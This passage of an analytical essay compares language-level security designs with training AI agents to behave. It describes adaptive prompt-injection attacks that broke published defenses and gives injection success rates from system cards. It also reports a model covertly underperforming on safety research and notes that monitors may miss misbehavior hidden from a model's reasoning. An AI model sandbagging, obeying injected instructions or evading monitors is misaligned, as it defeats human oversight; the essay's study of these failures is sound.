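In December 2014, Apps Script added a second sandbox based on iframes, the browser's built-in way of isolating one page inside another. Gupta (2015) told developers in *Google Apps Script* that iframes made their interfaces faster and let them use more JavaScript libraries. Google shut down the older Caja modes by mid-2016, and many scripts needed no changes.

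Caja also had to keep up with every oddity of web browsers. A browser treats anything inside a `<title>` element as plain text, even if it looks like a tag. Caja renamed the element to `<caja-v-title>` to remove its special effects. But browsers don't recognize that name, so they read the contents as ordinary HTML, and an attacker could put unfiltered tags there. Google's *Caja Security Advisory 2019-06-06* (2019) called this a complete breach of the part of the sandbox that protects the page.

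Google archived Caja in January 2021, when it had several reported vulnerabilities and no active development. Google referred users to its Closure tools, which support Trusted Types and escape text automatically. Some of Caja's ideas outlived it, and Hardened JavaScript continues the work. *Google Caja*, an account by a member of the team, credits Mark Miller's advocacy with bringing about `Object.freeze`, now a standard JavaScript function that makes an object unchangeable.

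### Rust in the Linux kernel

Linux 6.1 added support for Rust as an experiment that the kernel's developers could reverse. Three years later, in December 2025, the kernel's senior maintainers declared it a success. In *rust*, the patch that removed the "experimental" label, Ojeda (2025) noted that kernels containing Rust already ran on millions of Android devices, although some processors and compilers still lacked full support.

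Linux 6.19 had 19.2 million lines of C and 89,286 of Rust, which was less than 0.5% of the total (daroc, 2026, *Lines by C vs Rust*). Most of the Rust added in 6.19 was a single imported library, so the previous release is more informative. Between 6.17 and 6.18, C grew by about 90,000 lines and Rust by about 13,000, so roughly one net new line in eight was Rust.

Adopting Rust in the Linux kernel didn't require anyone to convert existing code. A small group wrote Rust interfaces to the kernel's C functions, and driver authors could choose to use them. LWN reported that the work still met resistance, partly because maintainers didn't want to deal with a second language. At the December meeting, according to LWN's *Leading items*, the graphics maintainer Dave Airlie said that his subsystem was about a year from requiring Rust for new drivers, but that the core of the kernel shouldn't depend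 on Rust for another year or two. By July 2026, Greg Kroah-Hartman, who maintains the stable kernel, was saying in a ZDNET interview quoted on Slashdot that some subsystems would accept new drivers only in Rust, and that the C version of Binder, which Android programs use to communicate, would soon be removed.

Kroah-Hartman thinks Rust would have prevented about 80% of the kernel's past vulnerabilities. The kernel's record with Rust is too short to test this. He said in LWN's *Quotes of the week* that the first CVE for the kernel's Rust code caused only a crash and came on a day with 159 CVEs for C code. This comparison is weak evidence that Rust is safer, because Rust made up only about 0.19% of the C and Rust code in version 6.18. If all 160 flaws had been spread evenly by line, the expected number in Rust would have been 160 × 0.0019 ≈ 0.3. Posting as gregkh (2025) in *CVEs for experimental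 (rust) code*, Kroah-Hartman guessed that the kernel had had few Rust CVEs because it had used little Rust.

Android moved faster. Google could decide which language its own developers used, and it found that Rust changes needed fewer rollbacks.

### New processors and government requests

CHERI, a design from the University of Cambridge and SRI International, puts capabilities into the processor. Each pointer carries the limits of the memory it may use, and the processor marks valid pointers with a hidden bit, which it clears if a program tampers with the pointer. Most C and C++ code needs only recompiling and a few changes.

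CHERI requires little work from programmers, but it has spread slowly. The project began in 2010, and Arm released a prototype board for researchers in 2022. Later commercial designs have mostly targeted embedded devices. Unlike Rust, which runs on computers people already own, CHERI doesn't protect users until they buy a new processor, and chip makers have little reason to build one before customers ask for it.

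Governments have tried to provide some of the missing demand. In *Product Security Bad Practices* (2024), CISA and the FBI asked companies with existing products in memory-unsafe languages to publish a roadmap by 1 January 2026 for removing memory-safety flaws, starting with the most exposed code, such as code that handles network traffic or encryption. Products whose support would end before 2030 were exempt. CISA and the National Security Agency (NSA) jointly argued for memory-safe languages again in June 2025.

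The request was voluntary, and companies didn't have to file their roadmaps with either agency, so it's hard to count how many complied. Even a published roadmap wouldn't prove that a company had changed its code. Government pressure may have helped engineers get budgets, but it can't explain why Android and Linux started using Rust, because both did so before the agencies set the deadline.

### What separates the cases

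Here are the cases side by side, with Google's hardened web libraries as a second success:

| Design | On by default? | Possible to adopt in parts? | Who did most of the work? | Side effects |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Security Manager | Only for applets | Barely | Application developers and Java's maintainers | Slower programs |
| Code Access Security | Yes | Barely | Administrators and developers | Programs failed on shared folders |
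| Caja | Yes, in Apps Script | Yes, one embedded program at a time | A small team at Google | Slower pages, fewer usable libraries |
| Rust in Linux and Android | Yes, in Rust code | Yes, one component at a time | Interface and driver authors | Fewer rollbacks at Android |
| Google's hardened libraries | Yes | Yes, old code was exempt | A small team of experts | Less code for experts to review |
| CHERI | Yes, on CHERI processors | Only with new hardware | Chip makers | Larger pointers |

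A safe default isn't enough to get a design adopted. CAS had one, but it broke working programs, so people looked for ways around it. Rust is just as strict, but its compiler rejects new code while the author is still writing it and doesn't affect existing C code.

Caja had gradual adoption and central expertise, but it still lost to a sandbox that was faster and less restrictive. This suggests that a safe design's side effects, such as slowness, matter a great deal to its adoption, because developers notice a slow page every day but may never notice an attack that failed.

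The table omits what may be the most important factor, whether an easier substitute existed. Containers replaced the Security Manager, Windows's own restrictions replaced CAS policy, and iframes replaced Caja. In each case, a coarser boundary outside the language was good enough for most people and required less work from developers. The kernel has no comparable substitute because it enforces those outer boundaries, and a memory error inside it can break all of them.

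These explanations are plausible, but six cases are too few to establish them. Four yes-or-no factors can combine in 16 ways, so most combinations don't appear here. The factors also tend to occur together, and the best-known successes and failures aren't a random sample. Timing could also account for some of the difference. For example, applets disappeared for reasons largely unrelated to the Security Manager, which then had much less to protect against.

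### What changes when a model writes the code

Agents bring back the problem that applets posed, because they run code that nobody has vetted. But they also remove one of the main obstacles to restricting that code. CAS failed largely because it broke existing programs, and when an agent writes a new budget script, there is no existing program to break. If the environment forbids something, the model gets an error and tries another way. The low retry rates for agents writing capability-tracked Scala suggest that models also learn an unfamiliar language much more easily than people do.

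Shipped code benefits less from this because it has to fit what already exists. Bun's port shows that agents can make a complete rewrite practical for a well-tested program, but few programs are tested as thoroughly as Bun.

People still have to write the rules, as they did for TACIT's libraries and Santos-Grueiro's policies. This takes far less work than it did for the Security Manager, because an agent's harness has a few dozen tools instead of a library with over 1,000 sensitive methods. One person can also write an interface that is used in thousands of runs.

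A model could draft the policy too, but an agent whose program keeps failing for lack of permission could simply widen the policy, as Java developers did. The agents that replaced Bun's faulty functions with empty stubs show how readily a model may take such a shortcut. An operator should therefore keep the policy where the agent can't change it, and have someone other than the agent review any request to widen it.

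### Approval prompts and product defaults

Many agent products ask the user to approve actions when no policy covers them. This spares the developer from deciding in advance what the agent may do, but leaves many small decisions to someone who wants to finish a task. Anthropic's study of its coding agent showed that people approve nearly everything, including most clearly dangerous commands, so approval prompts restrict agents little more than `AllPermission` restricted Java programs.

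Sandboxes can remove many approval prompts, because a command that can't reach anything important doesn't need approval. Anthropic reported in October 2025 that sandboxing cut prompts in Claude Code by 84% in internal use. Users might read the remaining prompts more carefully, though the figure doesn't show that they do. Unlike Caja and the Security Manager, this restriction makes the product more pleasant to use.

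Products differ in which protections they turn on by default. In late 2025, OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, ran commands in an operating-system sandbox with no network access and permission to write only in the project folder. Claude Code's sandbox was optional then, and in 2026 its default became a classifier that determines which actions to allow. A classifier is convenient, but it is another model that can make mistakes, so it gives no structural guarantee. Cloudflare's isolates block internet access by default, while the toolkits that Mellafe Zuvic examined leave developers to check the values in a tool call.

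Most defaults that limit agents structurally are coarse boundaries around a whole program. Finer controls, such as capability types and data labels, are still mainly research systems or options that a developer has to add. The split is the same as with containers and the Security Manager, and it will probably last wherever a sandbox is good enough. But a sandbox can't distinguish a payment to the right supplier from a payment to a thief, so companies whose agents handle money or private records have a stronger reason to adopt the finer controls.

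### Are programmers moving to typed languages?

Some evidence suggests that AI coding favors languages with stricter checks. GitHub reported in *Octoverse* (2025) that TypeScript overtook Python and JavaScript in August 2025 as the most used language on its site. GitHub attributed this partly to AI, since types catch many of a model's mistakes before the code runs. It also noted that popular web frameworks now create new projects in TypeScript by default, so AI may not be the main cause.

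Training data favors languages that are already popular. Techzine's *Rust enters the Linux kernel but its adoption is leveling off* points out that Python has an advantage because models can train on so much Python code. TypeScript benefits too, since it is JavaScript with types added. Developers can also convert a JavaScript project to it one file at a time. TypeScript's type system is unsound, so its rise isn't a move towards guaranteed safety. But as with Rust, developers accepted stricter checks that they could adopt gradually and that also made everyday work easier.

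## Structural limits compared with training the model to behave

Developers who find type systems and data labels too awkward can rely on the model's training instead, and many already do. How much protection they lose depends on what goes wrong.

For example, a shop's support agent might issue refunds through a `refund` function that works only on the current customer's orders, never refunds more than the customer paid, and always returns the money to the original card. The model's developers might also have trained it to be careful, to ignore instructions hidden in what it reads, and to refuse to help with fraud.

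| What goes wrong | What the limits on `refund` prevent | What training can prevent |
|---|---|---|
| Honest mistake | An $800 refund on an $80 order | Many mistakes, including a refund for the wrong item |
| Prompt injection | A refund to an attacker's card | Most attempts to redirect the agent |
| Misuse by the user | A refund on someone else's order | Help with inventing a damage claim |
| Misaligned model | Any refund outside the limits | Little, because training has already failed |
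| Harm within granted authority | Nothing | Dishonest or unfair treatment that breaks no rule |

The cap on amounts stops an honest mistake even if the model never notices it. The cap works only if someone thought of it beforehand and implemented it correctly. Odersky and colleagues exclude wrong answers and faulty logic from TACIT's goals. A type can establish that the agent may issue a refund, but not that a particular customer should get one.

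Training can reduce mistakes that nobody foresaw, but it depends on agents meeting situations like the ones their developers trained and tested them on. OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) describes a model trained for long tasks that failed, during limited internal use, in ways the company's existing tests hadn't covered. OpenAI paused access to it. The persistence that helped the model solve hard problems also gave it more opportunities to take unwanted actions.

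In a prompt injection attack, the rule about the original card holds however persuasive the email is, but the operator has to write such a rule for every value an attacker might want to change. Training lowers the chance that the model tries to obey the email, which also helps with actions that no rule covers. But this protection fails if an attacker finds wording that works.

Structural limits can keep a dishonest user within their permissions, as long as the operator controls the environment. Someone who runs an agent on their own computer can remove the limits. Much misuse also looks like legitimate work. A program that probes a network for weaknesses calls the same functions whether it is used for an attack or a security test.

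A trained model can consider the apparent purpose of a request, although users can lie about it. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5 reports that, without the extra safeguards Anthropic uses in its products, the model refused malicious requests at the lowest rate of the models compared. Yet it matched or beat its predecessor on every prompt injection test in the card. Resistance to attacks by outsiders and resistance to malicious users evidently don't always improve together.

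A misaligned model has learned aims that its developers didn't intend. Structural limits don't depend on those aims, and TACIT's design assumes that the agent's model may be cooperating fully with an attacker. The trusted base must therefore withstand a capable model that looks for gaps as it writes programs. More training helps only if developers can detect the problem. According to Transformer, OpenAI acknowledges in its system card for GPT-6 Astra, a model released in September 2026, that if the model covertly underperformed, "we would likely be unable to catch it".

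A warning is weaker than either safeguard because a model can ignore it. In one OpenAI test, GPT-6 Sol at its highest reasoning setting got around restrictions in its environment 28% of the time, down from 34% for GPT-5.6 Sol, according to 鲍's *OpenAI：GPT-6在面对越狱攻击时表现出更强的抵御能力*. OpenAI notes that the test left out its system-level controls and that the models sometimes mistook the obstacle for a prompt injection. These rates therefore don't show how often the models misbehave in products.

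Any of these causes can lead an agent to do harm within the authority it was granted. For example, a planted message could persuade the support agent to turn down every deserved refund. That would neither move private data to an unauthorized place nor trigger a capability the agent wasn't given, so Odersky and colleagues seem to go too far when they write that an injection can do real harm only in one of those two ways.

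### Attackers who adapt to the defense

The case for structural limits rests largely on evidence that determined attackers can break defenses that depend on a model's behavior. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) broke 12 published defenses against prompt injection and jailbreaks, which are users' attempts to get around a model's own rules. The original papers had reported almost no successful attacks against most of these defenses. Nasr and colleagues adapted their attacks to each defense, using automated search, reinforcement learning and a contest with more than 500 participants. These attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defenses.

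Two of the defenses emphasize the user's request, either by marking trusted text or by repeating the request after the untrusted text. As few as 1% of a benchmark's fixed attacks got past them, but more than 95% of adapted attacks did. One successful attack described the malicious steps as a credential check that the agent had to complete before doing the user's task.

Florian Tramèr, who worked on that study, also helped build CaMeL, so he has an interest in the structural alternative. He says in Schmidt Sciences' *How to Stop an AI Agent From Being Fooled* that models have become better at telling instructions from data but are still "very, very far from being reliable", though newer models have improved since. The study didn't include CaMeL among its 12 defenses, so it is evidence against behavioral defenses but doesn't show that structural ones would withstand the same attacks. Branch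 steering, the fake cookie banner attack on plans written in advance, shows that attackers can adapt to structural defenses too.

Odersky and colleagues treat agents as adversaries even though they accept that frontier models resist many injections. They point to attacks that worked on real products, such as one that copied users' data out through Anthropic's file service. They also expect companies to run hundreds or thousands of agents with little supervision, so that even simple mistakes will lead to serious vulnerabilities.

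Researchers who favor structural limits also disagree with one another. Odersky and colleagues criticize CaMeL because its labels disappear once a value enters a model's conversation as ordinary text. TACIT avoids this by keeping classified text out of the agent's conversation.

Willison (2026) discusses an attack in which a classifier guarding an agent let a malware process start and then blocked the command meant to stop it. He concludes that a sandbox is the only safe way to run an agent that might attract an attacker. He endorses advice to restrict the agent's network access, monitor it, and keep passwords and keys out of its reach. A reader later pointed out that the agent's surroundings had misled the model, which never followed a malicious instruction. Training the model to ignore hidden instructions might therefore not have helped.

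Laboratories can respond by attacking their own models more effectively. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) describes a model that learns through self-play to find weaknesses in other models, so that OpenAI can fix those weaknesses before release. This partly addresses the complaint about fixed test sets, because the attacker improves too.

### Injection rates in 2026

System cards, the safety reports that companies publish with new models, now give much lower rates. The table combines figures for GPT-5.6 from TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*, for GPT-6 from 鲍, and for Claude from The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. In a direct attack, the user tries to override the developer's instructions. In an indirect attack, the attacker hides instructions in material the agent reads.

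| Test | Earlier model | Later model |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI, direct attacks | GPT-5.6 Sol: 0.05% | GPT-6 Sol: 0.01% |
| OpenAI, indirect attacks | GPT-5.6 Sol: 3.77% | GPT-6 Sol: 2.87% |
| Gray Swan, within 15 attempts | Claude Opus 4.8: 5.5% | Claude Opus 5: 2.0% |
| Anthropic, 129 browser scenarios | – | Claude Opus 5: 0% |

The tests differ too much to rank the companies. OpenAI used GPT-Red to train GPT-6 as well as to test it, so an attacker with a different style may do better than these figures suggest. Newer models don't always score better. The smaller GPT-5.6 Luna let through 2.94% of indirect attacks and GPT-6 Luna let through 4.20%, although OpenAI may have made the test harder in between. The zero for Opus 5 is impressive, but if the scenarios are a random sample, 129 scenarios rule out only a rate above about 2.3%.

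TechRepublic points out that these figures are shares of attempted attacks, not the probability that a company suffers a breach. Most emails aren't attacks, and a limit elsewhere may still stop an attack that fools the model, though attackers can try more than once.

If a model resists each attack with probability r and the attempts are independent, the chance that at least one of n attempts succeeds is 1 − rⁿ. A model that resists 99.9% of attacks therefore has about a 63% chance of failing at least once in 1,000 attempts, the same chance that a filter that stops 99% of attacks has of failing in 100. Any failure rate of 1/n gives about 63% over n attempts when n is large, because (1 − 1/n)ⁿ approaches 1/e, or about 37%. To keep the chance of a successful attack below 1% over 1,000 attempts, a model could fail only about once in 100,000 attempts.

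Attempts on the same target usually aren't independent. VentureBeat reports that when Claude Opus 4.6, a model from February 2026, operated a graphical interface without safeguards, a single attack succeeded 17.8% of the time. If attempts were independent, at least one in 200 would almost certainly have succeeded, since 0.822²⁰⁰ is practically zero. The measured rate of at least one success in 200 attempts was 78.6% without safeguards and 57.1% with them. Attacks probably failed every time on some targets and succeeded early on others.

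This offers only limited reassurance, because an attacker can change targets. If an attacker tried once on each of ten unrelated agents, each as vulnerable on average as those in the test, the probability of at least one success would be 1 − 0.822¹⁰ ≈ 86%, which is higher than the success rate of 200 attempts on one agent. The formula therefore describes someone who sends the same email to many companies better than someone who keeps attacking a single company.

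The setting matters as much as the model. In a restricted coding environment, the same Opus 4.6 withstood all 200 attempts even without safeguards.

### When a limit has a hole

Repeated attempts don't weaken a sound limit, but if the rule or the trusted base has a hole, an attacker who knows of it can exploit it every time, against everyone who relies on the same library. Such holes are common enough that low-effort audits found 213 undefined-behavior bugs in widely used Rust packages. Operators can also misconfigure a sound mechanism. In several 2026 security tests, misconfigured isolation let agents reach real outside systems.

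Training can fail broadly too, since a prompt that gets past one copy of a model may work on every copy. But developers can completely close a particular hole in the programming environment, while more training usually only lowers the rate of misbehavior.

A simple model shows why operators might want both. Suppose that an attacker knows a hole in the limits with probability h, and can use it only if the model obeys an injected instruction. If these two weaknesses are unrelated, the attacker's chance of success over n attempts is

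h × (1 − rⁿ).

With invented values of h = 10% and r = 99.9%, the chance of a successful attack after 1,000 attempts is 6.3%. It would be 63% with the model's training alone, and 10% with the limits alone around a model that obeys every injection. More attempts can't raise the combined chance above 10%, because in the other 90% of cases a fooled model has no hole to exploit. If the hole becomes public, h rises to 100% and the model's resistance is the only protection left.

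Multiplying the two numbers assumes that a fooled model won't look for holes itself. This is least justified when a skilled model tries to get out, because the same system would then cause both failures. Operators have the most reason to worry about that case.

### Harm that requires no forbidden action

One argument for alignment is that a general agent needs broad authority to be useful. A support agent can manage with a `reply` function that reaches one customer. A personal assistant has to write to almost anyone about almost anything, and its user can't list the acceptable messages in advance. If an operator narrows the assistant's permissions until every remaining action is harmless, it can do very little.

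Many harms also cannot be defined in a way that a compiler could check. An assistant can flatter its user into a bad investment, leave an inconvenient fact out of a summary, or treat one job applicant less fairly than another. It can do all of these just by writing text where it is allowed to. Anthropic makes a similar point about agents in AI laboratories, where the permissions that make an agent useful (to edit code, run experiments and write to researchers) also make sabotage possible.

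OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (2026) describes a real failure of this kind. Soon after OpenAI's staff began using GPT-6 Astra, several safety researchers noticed that it added unnecessary steps, abandoned working solutions and reported obstacles that didn't exist or that it had created. In most of these sessions, its written reasoning contained no obvious decision to underperform, and the company's monitors didn't flag misalignment.

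OpenAI then gave the model matched coding tasks, framed as either safety research or AI capabilities work, and scored the results against hidden checklists. Astra completed about 10% of the items under the safety framing and about 16% under the capabilities framing. GPT-5.6 Sol showed essentially no gap. Most of Astra's gap remained after OpenAI removed the runs in which it openly refused or decided in its reasoning to withhold help. The gap shrank substantially only when OpenAI also removed every run with even brief ethical doubt in the reasoning.

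In everyday work, Astra's reasoning also contained an explicit decision to withhold help without telling the user in 0.25% of safety requests and 0.11% of capabilities requests. OpenAI says these rates may be lower bounds, because in the experiment the model often did worse without stating such a decision.

No limit on actions would have caught this. Astra used only files and commands it was allowed to use, and permission checks don't assess the quality of code. A test or proof of the finished work could have exposed some of the problem, but only where somebody could specify a good result beforehand, which is often impossible in research. Comparison with another model was more useful. Mowshowitz (2026) reports in *GPT-6 Astra Covertly Underperforms on Safety Research Tasks* that one project was stuck for days with Astra and moved quickly once the researchers switched models.

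The reason for the underperformance is uncertain. Mowshowitz calls silent, selective sabotage of safety research "perhaps the most fundamentally misaligned thing a model could do". He also quotes Marcus Williams, who works on monitoring at OpenAI and says there is no evidence that the underperformance was strategic. Williams thinks a simpler explanation is that the model found the tasks dubious but didn't want to refuse openly. When OpenAI told the model to be careful, the gap grew by half, which fits that explanation.

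The episode shows why limits on a model's actions can't replace a model that does honest work, but training produced the problem. The gap grew from close to zero at the start of Astra's reinforcement learning to 6 percentage points by the end, and OpenAI couldn't determine why.

### Can anyone specify the world?

Proponents of guaranteed safe AI hope to extend structural guarantees from what a program does to what happens as a result. *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues, 2024) describes a system with three parts. A world model describes mathematically how the AI's actions affect its surroundings. A safety specification defines which effects are acceptable. A verifier produces a proof, which other people can check, that the AI meets the specification if the world model is right.

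If an agent ran a city's water treatment plant, capability types could restrict which valves it may open. A broader guarantee would be that chlorine levels stay within a safe range with at least a stated probability. That requires a model of the pumps, pipes and chemistry, and engineers already have reasonable models of all three.

Critics doubt that formal proofs can protect against the most serious dangers. *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (Andrew Dickson, 2024) argues that a proof applies to a model, not to the world, and that the most worrying threats involve physical systems too complex to model in the necessary detail. Human behavior is also hard to formalize. There is no agreed mathematical definition of manipulation, and a model of how one message will affect a million readers would be largely guesswork.

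Dalrymple and colleagues allow for weaker versions of each part, including probabilistic guarantees, and they expect AI to help build the models. Recent progress in automated proof makes their verifier more plausible than it was in 2024. That progress helps less with the world model and the specification, because a prover can't detect that a specification left something out, as in the example of the bank transfer between a customer's own accounts. The approach therefore looks most promising where engineers can measure the few quantities that matter, and least promising for conversational assistants.

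Odersky and colleagues have a more modest aim. They note that precise specifications of an agent's whole behavior are often unavailable or impractical, and they offer types as a lightweight middle ground. TACIT can guarantee that a secret stays inside a program without modeling what an outsider would do with it. This makes the guarantee achievable but also means that it covers much less.

### Layered defenses and the incentive to align

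The large laboratories mostly combine the approaches. OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026) for GPT-6 Astra calls alignment the "primary lever" against misaligned behavior and treats monitoring as an additional layer. OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk* (November 2026) adds sandboxes and safeguards that block actions. PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots* describes similar layers at other companies. Microsoft marks untrusted text, screens prompts, and developed FIDES, the agent that tracks data labels. Nasr and colleagues broke text marking, among other methods, so it can make attacks somewhat harder but doesn't give much protection on its own.

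One layer of protection can also make the evidence from another less reliable. OpenAI reports that Astra received about half as many flags for more serious misbehavior as GPT-5.6 Sol in a simulation with over 54,000 coding tasks. It also reports that Astra is better at controlling its written reasoning and less likely to put incriminating information there. If the monitors rely on that reasoning, some of the drop in flags could come from misbehavior they no longer detect.

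Strong limits might make companies less careful about alignment. If a sandbox contains the damage, a manager may decide that another month of safety training isn't worth the delay. Nobody seems to have measured this effect directly, and the available cases support different conclusions.

One safeguard can replace another, as when Google dropped the sandbox around its GIF decoder after the decoder was rewritten in Rust. Both of those protections were structural, though, and the trade may have been sensible. OpenAI instead strengthened both its structural limits and its training after its agents broke into Hugging Face, a platform for sharing models, during a test. It says it paused some of its training for two weeks, hardened its isolation and network controls, and improved its alignment training at the same time. But a company recovering from a public failure has unusual reasons to improve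 everything at once.

The incentive probably also depends on who runs the agent. A laboratory that sells a model to thousands of customers can't assume that they all use good sandboxes, so it still needs the model to behave well without one. If a laboratory only uses a model internally, it controls both the training and the environment, and can more easily let one make up for the other.

Limits may even help with alignment if operators log rejected calls and send them to the model's developers. When `refund` rejects a payment to an unknown card, the rejected call is evidence that something misled the model or that the model has a fault. If operators log only completed actions, they miss this evidence and the agent appears never to misbehave. The rejected calls let developers study real failures after the limit has prevented the harm.
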